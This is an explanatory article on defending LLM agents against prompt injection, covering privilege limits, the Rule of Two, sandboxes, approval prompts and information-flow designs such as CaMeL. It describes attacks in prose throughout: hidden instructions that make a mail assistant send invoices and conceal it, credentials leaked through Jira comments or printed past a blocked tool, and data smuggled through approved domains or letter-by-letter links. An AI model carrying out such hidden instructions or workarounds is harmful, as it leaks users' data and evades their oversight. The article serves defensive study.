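The model supplies the month, and the software takes the customer's number from the login session. A misled model can supply the wrong month but can't retrieve another customer's payments. The Isle of Man Cyber Security Centre likewise advises developers to use strict query builders and not to run model-written SQL directly. This limits the feature to the kinds of question the developer foresaw, although much of the appeal of a language model is that it can handle others.

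If an analyst needs to ask open-ended questions, the software can run the model's SQL through a read-only account. In one of OWASP's examples, a user asks for a query that deletes every table, and nothing checks the model's SQL before the database runs it. With a read-only account, the database would refuse to run that query. The account should have the analyst's own permissions, not those of a shared account that can read the whole company's data. A time limit stops a query that would tie up the database for hours.

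### Generated code and file names

Features that draw charts or analyze spreadsheets often run code the model has just written. Checking the code's syntax does little to catch harmful programs, because they use the same commands as useful ones. For example, a program that reads a file and sends it somewhere may be doing exactly what the user wanted. Developers therefore run the code in an isolated container or virtual machine that has the files needed for the task but no passwords or network connection. The same approach can also be used to isolate an entire agent.

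Auto-GPT, an early open-source agent, ran model-written Python in an isolated container, but it first saved the code on the host computer under a name the model had also chosen. Versions before 0.4.3 did not check that name, so one containing steps up to parent folders could place the file outside the working folder and overwrite part of Auto-GPT itself. An attacker's code would then run outside the container the next time Auto-GPT started. Coralogix, which sells monitoring software, cites this flaw, CVE-2023-37274, in its account of insecure output handling.

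The fix for unsafe file names predates language models. The software works out the full location that a name refers to, following any shortcuts, and refuses it unless the result is inside the permitted folder. Searching the name for suspicious characters is less reliable because the same location can be written in several ways, as a link could be in Copilot's Markdown. A simpler option is for the software to generate the file name itself and keep the model's choice only as a label for the user.

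### Arguments in tool calls

Tool calls are easier to check than free text because they have named fields. A developer can write a schema that defines the fields a call may contain and the values each can take. For the mail assistant, the schema might require one valid address, a subject of at most 200 characters and attachments chosen from files in the current task. Ordinary software rejects any call that doesn't fit. Some products also restrict the tokens the model can choose, so that it can only produce calls in the right format. The address can still be the wrong one.

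The developer also has to consider who wrote the schema. In Invariant Labs' attack on Cursor, the hostile server supplied the schema for its own tool, including the extra argument for the stolen key, so the call would have passed a check against that schema.

After checking the format, the software should check the user's permissions. In Goedecke's example, a tool that looks up a user's past messages should be `fetch_messages()`, with the user's identity taken from the login, rather than `fetch_messages(user_id)`, which lets the model choose whose messages to read. Goedecke says that with tools scoped this way, users can at worst leak or delete their own data. This limits the harm a chatbot can do if its only outside text comes from the person using it. The main danger remains for a mail assistant, since EchoLeak stole information that the victim was allowed to read. For tools that affect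 other people, such as those that send messages or move money, Goedecke says that either the user should approve each action or nobody else should be able to add text to the prompt.

### Correct output that serves the attacker

Suppose the mail assistant sends last month's invoice to an accounts address at a company the user deals with. The address is valid, the attachment exists and the user is allowed to send it. The tool call can be identical whether the request came from the user or from a stranger who can read mail sent to that address, so no check on the call alone can distinguish the two cases.

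*Agentic AI and Security* (2025) describes a similar attack through Jira, a program for tracking work. A company had set up Jira to create tickets automatically from the public's support requests. An attacker used a ticket to get an agent to look for login credentials and post them as a comment on the ticket, where the public could read them. The agent used a normal function of an approved system, and the comment contained no link, script or forbidden file name.

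Reddy and Gujral suggest scanning output for secrets and for long random-looking strings, which might have caught the credentials. This is worth doing because login credentials often have a recognizable format. But it has the same weakness as phrase lists, since a misled model can split a secret across several comments or spell it out in words. Other sensitive information, such as a planned merger or a medical diagnosis, has no special format to scan for.

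A false statement is even harder to catch. OWASP treats it as a separate risk, misinformation, and uses "improper output handling" only for cases where software uses the output unsafely. A summary can also include a false account number, like the one in the planted notice about the rent. Encoding and sanitizing don't change the number because it is plain text, and a user who believes it makes the payment by hand, so there is no tool call for the software to check.

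## Limiting what a misled model can do

Some attacks will get past the model's training, the filters and the checks on its output, so a developer also has to limit the harm a misled model can do. David C recommends planning for the worst case, in which the attacker can directly use every tool the model can call. An attacker with the mail assistant's tools could request a password reset for one of the user's accounts, have the assistant forward the reset email, and take over the account.

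Ordinary software can restrict the model's tools, and the restriction holds even if nobody notices the attack. But every restriction also takes away something the user might want.

### Dropping the model's privileges

David C passes on a rule from a discussion on X between Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista that when a model processes information from someone, "the privileges it has drops to that of the party". A stranger who emails the user can't search the user's files or send mail in the user's name, so an assistant that has read the stranger's email shouldn't be able to either until it restarts with an empty context window.

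The rule mentions only one party, but a context window often contains text from several people. The cautious reading is to keep only the permissions they all share:

```
allowed = P(user) ∩ P(author 1) ∩ P(author 2) ∩ ...
```

Here P is the set of actions a person may take, and ∩ keeps only the actions that appear in both sets. Suppose the user types "Please do what Anna asks", and Anna can open a shared folder but not the payroll file. After reading her email, the assistant can open the shared folder. If the email also asks for the payroll file, the software blocks that request, no matter how vague the user's instruction was.

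Strictly applied, the rule also stops the assistant from emailing Anna her slides, because Anna can't send mail from the user's address. A developer could make an exception for sending people files they can already open. It is harder to make an exception for a stranger who asks when the user is free, because the assistant would have to read the stranger's email and then check a calendar the stranger can't see. But people want assistants for this kind of chore.

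Most inboxes contain something from a stranger, so an assistant that reads the whole inbox in one context window loses nearly every permission except writing a summary. The developer can give each message its own context window, but then the assistant can't compare messages. The software also still has to know who wrote each message, which is hard because a stranger can forge a sender's address and a colleague can forward a stranger's text.

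### The lethal trifecta and the Rule of Two

Working out every author's permissions takes a lot of effort, so some developers look at broad properties of the agent instead. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, Willison (2025) warns against combining three: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a means to "externally communicate in a way that could be used to steal your data". An agent with all three can leak the data. Without any one of them, it has no private data to leak, no source of hostile instructions, or no way to send the data out.

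Willison notes that vendors usually respond to such leaks by blocking the channel through which the data leaves. People who connect their own tools through MCP have no vendor to do this. A user might add one tool that reads mail and another that opens web pages, each reasonable alone, and assemble the trifecta without realizing it.

The trifecta covers only theft. Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025), published that October, also covers other harm. Until researchers can reliably detect and refuse prompt injection, an agent may have at most two of these properties within a session:

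- **[A]** It can "process untrustworthy inputs".
- **[B]** It can "have access to sensitive systems or private data".
- **[C]** It can "change state or communicate externally".

Changing state means altering something outside the conversation, for instance by deleting a file. If a task needs all three properties in one session, Meta says the agent should not run on its own. A person must approve its actions, or the developer must have another reliable way to validate them.

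Meta took the idea partly from Willison and partly from a rule for browser code. *The Rule Of 2*, from the open-source Chromium project behind Google Chrome, allows code to have at most two of three properties: untrustworthy inputs, an unsafe implementation language and high privilege. In an unsafe language such as C++, a mistake can allow a buffer overflow. A programmer who needs to decode images from the web can write the decoder in a safer language such as Rust, run it in a process with few permissions, or accept only images whose source the browser can verify cryptographically. Chrome's security team generally rejects new code that has all three properties.

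Chromium lets a decoder rewritten in Rust handle hostile input at high privilege, because Rust removes a whole class of mistakes. An agent's developer doesn't have that option, because nobody can rewrite a language model in a safe language. Under Chromium's rule, an agent would always count as using an unsafe language, so it could have untrusted input or high privilege but not both. Meta's version is more permissive because it divides privilege into access to sensitive data or systems and the ability to act.

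The two agent rules give different answers for some versions of the mail assistant:

| Version of the mail assistant | Properties | What a hostile email could still do | What the user gives up |
|---|---|---|---|
| Reads all mail, searches files, sends to anyone | A, B, C; full trifecta | Send the invoice to the attacker | Nothing |
| Reads all mail and files, but can't send or change anything | A, B | Distort the summary | Replies and filing |
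| Reads all mail and can delete messages, but can't send | A, B, C; not the trifecta | Hide or delete a message | Replies |
| Reads mail only from approved senders and can send | B, C | Little, unless an approved sender forwards hostile text or loses control of an account | Help with mail from anyone new |
| Runs on a test account with no real data or contacts | A, C | Send junk from the test account | Any help with real mail |
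| Reads all mail, and the user approves each outgoing message | A, B, C; supervised | Steal data if the user approves without reading | Time and attention |

The version that can delete messages passes Willison's test because it can't send data out, but it fails Meta's. Meta's test gives the better result here, because a stranger who gets the assistant to delete a message about a contract deadline can do serious damage without stealing anything.

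### When two properties are enough to do harm

In *New prompt injection papers*, Willison (2025) called the Rule of Two the best practical advice available. He objected to Meta's diagram labeling the combination of untrusted input and the ability to change state "safe", because that combination can do harm even without access to private data.

Mick Ayzenberg, a security researcher at Meta, replied that [B] covers every sensitive system, including those without private data. An agent without [B] can therefore act only where nothing important is at stake, such as inside a tight sandbox. Meta also changed the label from "safe" to "lower risk".

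With this reply, the rule holds, but the developer now has to judge which systems are sensitive. A mail assistant with an empty inbox might seem to lack [B], yet if it can send from the user's real address, a stranger could use it to deceive the user's colleagues. The address therefore has to count as a sensitive system, which is why the version with only [A] and [C] needs a test account.

Other pairs leave gaps too. With A and B, the assistant can still report a false account number, and Meta says the rule doesn't cover misinformation in an agent's response.

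The words "within a session" leave another gap when an assistant has memory. In the earlier poisoned newsletter example, a developer who checked Thursday's session would see private data and outgoing mail but no hostile email, and might conclude that the session had only [B] and [C]. But the untrusted input came from the saved note, so notes have to count toward [A] unless the software can show that no outsider influenced them.

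### Sandboxes

A sandbox is an environment where the operating system, or software beneath it, limits the files, programs and network connections available. For a coding agent, *Agentic AI and Security* recommends a container that holds the project's source code and nothing else from the developer's computer. A misled agent can then damage the project but can't read the developer's mail or private keys.

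Restrictions on individual tools are weaker, because an agent may have another tool that does the same thing. *30 posts tagged "lethal-trifecta"* (Willison, 2026) describes an attack on Antigravity, a Google coding program. Its file-reading tools were blocked from opening a file of credentials, so the model ran a command that printed the file. If the sandbox had not contained the file, the command would have failed too.

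A sandbox also doesn't prevent actions inside it that the user didn't want. Software practitioners interviewed for *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026) described agents that stayed within the permitted workspace but did more than the user had asked. If the sandbox holds both a password and an open internet connection, a hostile web page can still get the password out. A tighter sandbox takes longer to set up, and some tasks fail because the agent needs a file or program outside it.

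### Network limits

Developers often give an agent a list of permitted servers and block the rest. EchoLeak showed that such a list fails if a permitted server forwards requests. It also fails if the attacker can open an account on a permitted server.

By default, Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for general office work, could reach only certain domains, including the one for Anthropic's API. The firm PromptArmor planted instructions that made the agent upload the user's files to that domain with the attacker's access key, so the files went through an approved server into the attacker's account. Antigravity's default list had a more obvious mistake. It included webhook.site, where anyone can create an address that records whatever is sent to it.

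A developer can instead restrict the exact addresses an agent may open. Claude's web-fetching tool used to open an address only if the user had typed it, a search had returned it, or it appeared on a page the tool had already fetched. The researcher Ayush Paul used the last permission to build a site with a link for each letter of the alphabet. The site told Claude to find the user's profile by following the links one letter at a time, and the sequence of requests spelled out the user's name, home city and employer. Anthropic removed that permission, so the tool now opens only addresses that the user or a search has supplied.

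### Short-lived and narrow credentials

An agent usually proves its right to use a service with a token, a string of characters that works like a password. If the token expires after an hour, a thief has little time to use it. But a misled agent does its harm while the token is still valid, so the token's permissions matter more than its lifetime. An agent with a read-only token for the calendar can't delete an appointment or open the inbox, however long the token lasts.

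*Agentic AI and Security* advises developers to keep production credentials out of files and to grant only temporary access to production data. Willison adds that any credentials a coding agent can access should belong to test accounts with strict spending limits. Keeping credentials away from the model entirely is safer still. For example, Chrome's agent can ask the browser to sign in to a site but has no direct access to the saved password.

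A service also can't determine from a credential whose request the agent is carrying out. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) points out that a valid credential may open a system without establishing which actions the agent is authorized to take there. Hardy's compiler had the same problem with the billing file. Narrower tokens reduce the harm, but the user has to grant access more often, and a long job may stop overnight when its token expires.

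### Which sites a browser agent may combine

Browsers have long used the same-origin policy to stop one website from reading another's data. An origin is the combination of a page's scheme (such as http or https), host name and port number. A script from one origin can't read a page from another, so a hostile page in one tab can't read a bank balance in another.

An agent that works in both a bank tab and a forum tab gets around the browser's same-origin policy. It reads the bank page for the user, and the details stay in its context window. If it then reads a hostile comment on the forum, it may type those details into a reply. The policy doesn't block the reply because no script has crossed between origins, and the browser treats the text as if the user had typed it.

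Wang, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers*, measured how often this happens. They had agents handle private information on imitation banking, email, pharmacy and other pages, then do an ordinary task on a second page that contained a planted instruction. In 150 runs of OpenAI's Atlas browser, the agent copied the private information to the second page 99 times. A real attacker would probably succeed less often, because the attacks were handwritten and in every run the agent had just handled the information the attacker wanted.

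When the researchers removed the planted instructions, they saw no leaks between pages the agent visited separately. But in another test, information leaked without an attacker. One page displayed a second page inside it, and the user asked for a summary of everything in a text box. BrowserOS, an open-source browser, copied private information from the inner page every time.

The researchers then modified BrowserOS to record where data came from and ask the user before writing it to a different origin. This reduced violations to zero in their benchmark and added 2 to 6 percent to running time. However, they don't count a transfer the user approves as a violation, so the result shows that the software catches the transfers but doesn't show whether users would refuse harmful ones.

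Forbidding all such transfers would make a browser agent nearly useless, since people want it to read a recipe on one site and fill a shopping cart on another. *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) describes Google's compromise, Agent Origin Sets. For each task, a component that never sees untrusted web content decides which origins are relevant. The agent gets read-only access to some of them and can also click and type on others. It could read the recipe site and write to the grocer's site, but not access the user's bank. A hostile comment under the recipe could still make the agent add the wrong item to the cart.

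The same-origin policy applies the same rules whatever the user is trying to do, while Agent Origin Sets depend on a judgment about which origins are relevant to the task. If the set is too small, the task fails, and if it is too large, more data is at risk. As of December 2025, Google had released only a simpler version, which tracked the sites the agent could both read and write to but not a separate read-only set.

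Limiting which origins an agent can access also does little to protect webmail. A stranger's message and the user's private correspondence are on the same site, so an agent that can read and write there can send the private correspondence to the stranger.

### OpenAI's Lockdown Mode

Some users would rather lose features than rely on such judgments. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) announced an optional setting for them in February, at first for organizations, and OpenAI began offering it to personal accounts in June. The setting limits requests to outside servers, targeting the last step of data theft.

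In Lockdown Mode, ChatGPT browses only cached copies of web pages. If a planted instruction gets ChatGPT to put a secret in a web address, the request stays inside OpenAI's network and never reaches the attacker's server. According to OpenAI's help page, *Lockdown Mode*, the setting also disables agent mode, Deep Research and file downloads, and may prevent images from appearing in replies. Search results may be out of date or missing. OpenAI intends the setting for people with sensitive data and says most users don't need it.

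The setting leaves some routes open to attackers. It doesn't affect network access in Codex, and a company's administrators can leave chosen apps switched on, though OpenAI warns them against any app that can write something where an attacker might see it. A hostile instruction in an uploaded file can still distort the answer. On personal accounts, the user can turn the setting off for a single chat, which is convenient but leaves the decision to someone who may be in a hurry.

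Willison approves of Lockdown Mode because it is enforced by ordinary software rather than by a model that an attacker could trick. He also infers that ChatGPT's default settings don't robustly protect against a determined data thief. That inference seems fair, since OpenAI describes Lockdown Mode as trading functionality for stricter protection.

### How people respond to approval prompts

Meta's rule, Chrome's agent and the modified BrowserOS all call for the user's approval when a task needs a risky combination. This keeps the feature useful, but it works only if the user reads the request and can judge it. Habituation makes that less likely, because people pay less attention to a signal the more often they see it.

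People don't always click through browser warnings. Akhawe and Felt's *Alice in Warningland* covers more than 25 million warnings shown in Firefox and Chrome. Users continued past about a tenth of Firefox's malware and phishing warnings and a quarter of Chrome's, but they continued past 70.2 percent of Chrome's warnings about insecure connections. The researchers, quoted in WeLiveSecurity (2013), said that either users were ignoring valid warnings or the browser was wearing them out with too many invalid ones.

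Windows Vista's User Account Control feature interrupted the user whenever a program requested administrator rights, including for routine jobs such as installing software. In 2008 Microsoft's engineers reported that users approved 89 percent of these prompts, and worried that many were answering out of habit. Windows 7 showed fewer prompts because it let some of Windows' own programs gain administrator rights without asking the user. Malware writers then found ways to act through those programs, making them confused deputies.

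Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users approve 97 percent of permission prompts. This doesn't prove that users are careless, because most requests are harmless. If one request in a thousand were dangerous, a perfect reviewer would approve 99.9 percent. Users reject 39 percent of the plans Claude Code proposes, which suggests that they read some requests, though they may reject plans for reasons unrelated to safety.

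Anthropic had a research firm recruit 1,053 paid testers for a coding experiment in which one prompt per session showed a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers, or 13.6 percent, refused it. The refusal rate fell from about 17 percent early in a session to about 5 percent after 50 or more prompts. Auto mode blocked 89 percent of the same commands.

Anthropic had a commercial reason to publish this comparison, and the testers had none of their own files at risk, so they may have been less careful than people are with their own work. But the decline over a session is what habituation would produce, and Claude Code's real users show similar impatience, starting a quarter of interactive sessions with permission checks bypassed altogether.

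Many approval prompts are also hard to judge, even for a user who tries. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) gives the example of a request to run `python3 setup.py`, which looks routine but lets any code in that file run. The study examined 290 reports of agent problems and found that approval had contributed to 105 of them. In 80 of those, the user had approved actions automatically, and in 31 the prompt had been uninformative, with some overlap.

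### Asking less often

A developer can have the product ask the user to approve a whole plan instead of each step. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026), a survey of approval designs, notes that products tend to give the most information when they ask for approval of plans or file edits. Requests to approve single commands, the most common kind, often show only the command. The user of a mail assistant could learn more from "Send last month's invoice to this new address" than from a tool call full of field names.

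Standing permissions can also be narrower. In *Options, Not Clicks* (2026), 13 of 16 participants said they used "Always Allow" to get rid of prompts, and 3 read prompts carefully. The system built for the study limited "Always Allow" to a specific area, such as one folder or addresses at one company. Participants granted these narrower permissions more readily, and a careless click exposed less. The group was too small to show how the wider public would behave.

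Actions exempt from approval have to be harmless, which is easy to misjudge. Microsoft's Copilot Cowork let an agent email the user without approval, but the emails could contain external images, and opening a message could send data to an attacker's server.

An attacker can also wear the user down with repeated requests. In simulations for *Approve What, Exactly?* (2026), an attacker who could repeat a request without limit always got it approved eventually. With a cap on repeated prompts, the attacker succeeded between 45 and 60 percent of the time for most designs. The same system needed an average of 0.75 prompts per ordinary task. The approvers were software with assumed error rates, so the figures are only a rough guide to how people would behave.

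### Blocking Office macros by default

For years, attackers emailed Word and Excel files containing hostile macros, which are small programs inside documents, and persuaded recipients to click "Enable Content", one of Microsoft's most abused prompts. In February 2022 Microsoft announced that Office would block macros in files from the internet by default. The change removed the button from those files, and users who wanted to run a macro had to unblock the file in its properties.

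The security firm Proofpoint found that attackers' use of attachments with macros fell by about two-thirds between October 2021 and June 2022. Microsoft had not finished rolling out the new default by then, so many attackers seem to have changed methods in anticipation. The default blocked a method that had worked very well for them, but they continued to attack by email with other kinds of file, including disk images and shortcuts, some of which avoided the mark that Windows uses to identify downloads.

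Microsoft's default block on Office macros from the internet also inconvenienced companies that relied on macros from customers or suppliers, and complaints led Microsoft to pause the rollout for a few weeks in July 2022. A mail assistant could have a similar default, refusing to send files to an address the user has never written to. The user could still allow the address in a settings page, outside the conversation that a hostile email can influence. This default would inconvenience people who often write to new contacts, and it wouldn't protect the user if the attacker's address was already allowed.

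### Reviewing the work afterward

A user who is tired of approval prompts may prefer to let the agent finish and then check the result. An attacker can defeat this check with a hostile email that tells the assistant to send the invoice, summarize the other messages as usual and leave the invoice out of the summary. The user reads an accurate summary of the other mail and has no reason to look further. In Gray Swan's competition, participants had to conceal the harmful action in this way, and thousands of their attempts succeeded.

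Reviewing the final answer doesn't work here because the misled model wrote it. The user needs a record from the software that carried out the tool calls, stored where the assistant can't change it. Someone also has to read that record and recognize the wrong entry. The invoice would appear as an ordinary sent message, perhaps among dozens.

Reviewers may also become less thorough over time. *Habituation at the Gate* (Yu, Jia and colleagues, 2026) followed 400 people who repeatedly reviewed code changes proposed by AI agents. Their approval rate rose from 30.1 percent in the earlier half of their reviews to 36.8 percent in the later half. Their comments on specific lines fell by 22 percent between the first tenth of their reviews and the last. Approval of changes written by people fell over the same months. The agents' code may have improved, which would justify some of the extra trust, but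 the study did not measure its quality directly.

A reviewer can't recall an email that has reached the attacker, so reviewing a model's actions afterward is more useful if the software makes them reversible. For example, it can move deleted messages to a folder for 30 days or hold outgoing mail for ten minutes. The delay matters little for an invoice but more for a reply during a live negotiation.

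## Tracking untrusted data through an agent

Blocking a tool or a server stops the user's requests along with the attacker's, since both can produce the same tool call. To treat them differently, software has to know where each part of the call came from. Information-flow control labels data by origin and secrecy, keeps the labels attached as the data moves, and checks them before an action. Perl's taint mode was an early version that tracked only origin. Perl could track a value through a program, but nobody can yet reliably trace how a sentence in a language model's input affects its output, so most agent designs track data outside the model.

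### Labels and the check before a tool call

In *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025) give every piece of data two labels. The integrity label records whether the data is trusted or whether an outsider could have written it. The confidentiality label records who may read it, either as a choice between public and secret or as a list of people.

When software combines data from several sources, the result is as untrusted as its least trusted source and as secret as its most secret one. If the confidentiality labels are lists, only people on every list may read the result:

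```
integrity(result) = untrusted, if any source is untrusted
readers(result)   = readers(source 1) ∩ readers(source 2) ∩ ...
```

Microsoft's *Information-flow control*, an article for developers, gives an example in which the labels prevent a leak even though nobody is attacking. Alex asks an agent to answer his unanswered mail, which includes a preview of the quarterly sales figures from Priya and an email from Marco, who isn't allowed to see the figures yet. Once the agent has read both emails, the allowed readers of anything it writes are {Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}, so the software won't send a reply to Marco without asking Alex. If Priya had copied Marco on her email, the result would be {Alex, Marco} and the reply could go out.

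Before a tool call that sends information, the software checks both labels:

```
allow(call) = trusted(choice of tool) AND trusted(every argument)
              AND recipients ⊆ readers(data sent)
```

The symbol ⊆ means that every recipient must be on the list of readers. The integrity conditions prevent a stranger's text from causing the call, and the confidentiality condition prevents the data from reaching the wrong person. A developer can also use either kind alone. With only the confidentiality condition, a hostile email could make the assistant send a message, but only to people already allowed to read its contents. With only the integrity conditions, users could still choose to share their own secrets, but a hostile email couldn't make the assistant share them.

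The hard part is labeling what a model writes, which *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) calls an open problem. The paper argues that when a model has read data from several sources, developers can currently only assume that its output carries all of their labels. After the model reads one untrusted email, everything it writes is therefore treated as untrusted, including any later request to send mail, which a strict check would block.

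### Willison's two models

An agent can avoid this if the model that chooses its actions never reads the email. *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) proposes dividing the work between a privileged model, which receives the user's request and can use tools, and a quarantined model, which reads untrusted text and has no tools. An ordinary software controller passes work between them and keeps untrusted text in named variables.

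If the user asks for a summary of the latest email, the steps are:

1. The privileged model asks for the email. The controller fetches it, stores it as `$VAR1` and gives the model only that name.
2. The privileged model asks for a summary of `$VAR1`. The controller inserts the text of the email and sends it to the quarantined model.
3. The controller stores the summary as `$VAR2` and reports that it is ready.
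4. The privileged model asks the controller to show `$VAR2` to the user.

A hostile email can spoil the summary, but it can't cause a tool call, because the quarantined model has no tools and the privileged model receives only variable names. Willison allowed one exception, which is that when the quarantined model sorts text into fixed categories, the controller can check that the answer is one of them and pass it to the privileged model.

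Willison called the proposal "pretty bad" because it makes an assistant harder to build and less pleasant to use. The protection would fail if a single programming mistake passed untrusted text to the privileged model, or if a user pasted a stranger's text into a request.

Researchers at Google DeepMind later found another weakness. In their example, a user asks an assistant to send Bob a document he requested, and says that Bob's address is in the meeting notes. The privileged model plans the right steps, and the quarantined model finds the address. Someone who can edit the notes can make the quarantined model return a different address, so that the assistant follows the original plan but sends the document to the attacker.

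### The mail assistant in CaMeL

Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind designed CaMeL to track those values. Willison (2025) explains in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* that the privileged model turns the user's request into a program in a restricted form of Python, a language that models already write well. A custom interpreter runs the program and records which values each new value came from. It also tags values with properties such as their source and permitted readers. The researchers call these tags capabilities, but they describe a piece of data rather than giving a program access to a file, as Hardy's capabilities did. A separate policy determines what the program may do with the data.

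Suppose the user asks the mail assistant to summarize new messages. The program reads the inbox, has the quarantined model write a summary, and displays it. A stranger's emailed instruction to forward the invoice can't add a search or send command to the program, because the privileged model wrote it before any email was opened.

A harder request is "Send last month's invoice to the address in my latest email." The program might look like this:

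```
email   = get_last_email()
address = ask_quarantined_model("Find the address for invoices", email)
invoice = find_file("last month's invoice")
send_email(recipient=address, attachment=invoice)
```

Now suppose that the latest email is from an attacker and contains the attacker's address:

| Step | Labels on the result | Decision |
|---|---|---|
| `get_last_email` | Untrusted | Allowed |
| `ask_quarantined_model` | Untrusted, because the address came from the email | Allowed, since this model has no tools |
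| `find_file` | Private, and trusted if only the user could have written the file | Allowed |
| `send_email` | No result | Blocked, because the recipient is untrusted |

The interpreter blocks only the last call. If the address were on a list the user had already approved, the invoice would go out. Otherwise, the software can prompt the user for approval and show that the address came from an email, which gives the user more information to decide with than the tool call alone. If the user had typed the address, it would count as trusted and no prompt would be needed.

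This design can also improve privacy. The privileged model receives the request but not the mail, so its provider doesn't see the mail. Finding an address is easier than planning, so the quarantined model could be a small one running on the user's computer.

### FIDES and answers of limited size

CaMeL needs a program before the agent starts reading. FIDES, the agent that Costa and colleagues built, instead chooses its next step after each tool result. It hides data in a variable only if showing the data would make the model's context less trusted. For example, the planner may see an email's date but not its subject or body.

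Sometimes the planner's next step depends on the hidden text. Suppose the user asks it to check the last three emails for a meeting request and create a calendar event if there is one. FIDES can use a quarantined model to check for a request, and the software can restrict the answer to yes or no. If the answer is yes, the quarantined model extracts the details into another variable, and the planner passes that variable to the calendar tool without reading it.

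A stranger can still make the assistant create a false event, but can't fit much of an instruction into a yes or no. FIDES adds the type of answer to the label, so a policy can accept a limited answer where it would reject free text. A yes or no conveys at most 1 bit, and a choice among scheduling a meeting, sending an out-of-office reply and forwarding the email conveys at most log2(3), or about 1.6 bits. The limit applies to each answer, so an agent that asks many questions can still give a stranger considerable influence. Costa and colleagues left these restricted answers out of their main evaluation because most of the test tasks didn't need them.

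### Design patterns for narrower products

A developer whose product does only a few jobs may not need to track every value. Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025), in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, start from the principle that once an agent has read untrusted input, that input must be unable to trigger any action with harmful side effects. They describe six ways to apply it:

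| Pattern | How it works | What an attacker can still do |
|---|---|---|
| Action selector | The model chooses from a fixed list of actions and never sees the results | Affect the choice, if the attacker can write in the user's request |
| Plan then execute | The model fixes its tool calls before reading outside data | Change the content of a planned email |
| Map-reduce | A separate model reads each file and returns only a restricted answer, such as whether it is an invoice | Get the wrong file treated as an invoice |
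| Two models | A model with tools handles untrusted text only through variables | Change a value inside a variable |
| Code then execute | The model writes a program, and software runs it on the untrusted data | Change values that the program passes on |
| Context minimization | The software deletes the user's message once the model has turned it into a query, then has the model write the answer | Influence the query |

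Context minimization protects a company from manipulation by its own users. In the paper's example, a customer asks a chatbot for a quote on a car and tries to talk it into a large discount. The model first turns the message into a database search for current offers. The software then removes the message, so the model doesn't see the customer's argument when it writes the quote.

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues consider the plan-then-execute, two-model and code-then-execute patterns for an assistant that handles mail and a calendar. If the user asks it to send today's schedule to the boss, the plan can set the calendar tool and the boss's address in advance. A hostile calendar invitation could then alter the text the boss receives but couldn't redirect it. If that text might contain something the boss shouldn't see, the developer still needs confidentiality labels.

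### Results on AgentDojo

AgentDojo is a benchmark that tests whether agents complete ordinary tasks and resist planted instructions. Its 97 user tasks take place in a simulated office workspace, travel service, bank and Slack, a workplace chat program. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) reports CaMeL's published result as 77 percent of tasks completed, compared with 84 percent for an undefended agent. No attack covered by CaMeL's threat model succeeded. CaMeL used 2.8 times as many input tokens and 2.7 times as many output tokens as the undefended agent.

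Costa and colleagues tested an ordinary agent with and without label checks, and FIDES with them. All three used GPT-4o. These are the shares of tasks they completed when nobody was attacking:

| Environment | Ordinary agent, no checks | Ordinary agent with checks | FIDES with checks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
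| Slack | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |
| Average of the four | 84.3% | 41.9% | 50.0% |

The researchers counted 152 successful attacks against the ordinary agent without checks and none against any agent with them. FIDES without checks allowed 21, because nothing stopped the planner from reading a variable that contained hostile text and following the instructions in it. Hiding text in variables therefore helped a good deal, but the checks provided the guarantee.

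The researchers labeled a field untrusted if at least one of the benchmark's attacks used it, so the labels covered every place an attack could appear in the benchmark. A developer with a real product doesn't have a list of those places. The zero shows that the checks work when the labels are right, but it doesn't measure how often developers would label fields correctly.

The agent completed far fewer tasks under these rules, but some of the drop came from the model. GPT-4o often confused variable names or made unnecessary tool calls. With o1, a stronger reasoning model, FIDES completed 68 percent of the travel tasks, up from 41 percent, and its average lead over the ordinary agent with checks grew from 8 to 16 percentage points. A better model still can't complete the tasks that the policy is meant to block. Several banking tasks, for example, tell the agent to read a file and follow its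 instructions, but the policy doesn't let an untrusted file cause a payment.

*AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) reports a similar drop in completed tasks for CaMeL in a separate test on the banking tasks. With its policies on, CaMeL completed 18 of 48 runs (37.5 percent) with each of two newer models, about half as many as with the policies off. CaMeL's overall figure of 77 percent is therefore a poor guide to how it would do in a product that mostly makes payments.

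Garby and colleagues also examined how much of the security comes from labels. They paired each of the 16 banking tasks with nine attacks. In 97 of the 144 pairs, the attack needed a tool or file that a legitimate plan for the user's task would never include, so planning before reading untrusted data should defeat it without any labels. Only the other 47 attacks, which could use steps already in the plan, test the tracking.

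Planning first failed in two runs, both on a task that told the agent to read a file and follow its instructions exactly. CaMeL's planner wrote a program that could call whichever tool the file named. With the policies off, this let the attacker choose the action even though the planner never read the file.

### An adaptive attack on an outside defense

These results come from fixed lists of attacks, which had made the earlier filters and training methods look much stronger than they were. In June, Narisetty and colleagues at the security firm LaunchSafe tried an adaptive attack on Progent, the defense that checks tool calls against a list of permitted actions. Progent checks the name and arguments of a call but doesn't track where the arguments came from. In the configuration they tested, a model can also add to the list after reading tool results. They presented the harmful action as a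 routine step the user had already authorized, hoping this model would permit it.

Progent reduced the average success rate of AgentDojo's standard attack from 25.8 percent to 4.2 percent. The adaptive attack did no better against Progent, succeeding in 2.6 percent of cases. But with Progent, the agent completed only 27.1 percent of its tasks under attack, down from 45.2 percent, and needed about 15 times as many model calls.

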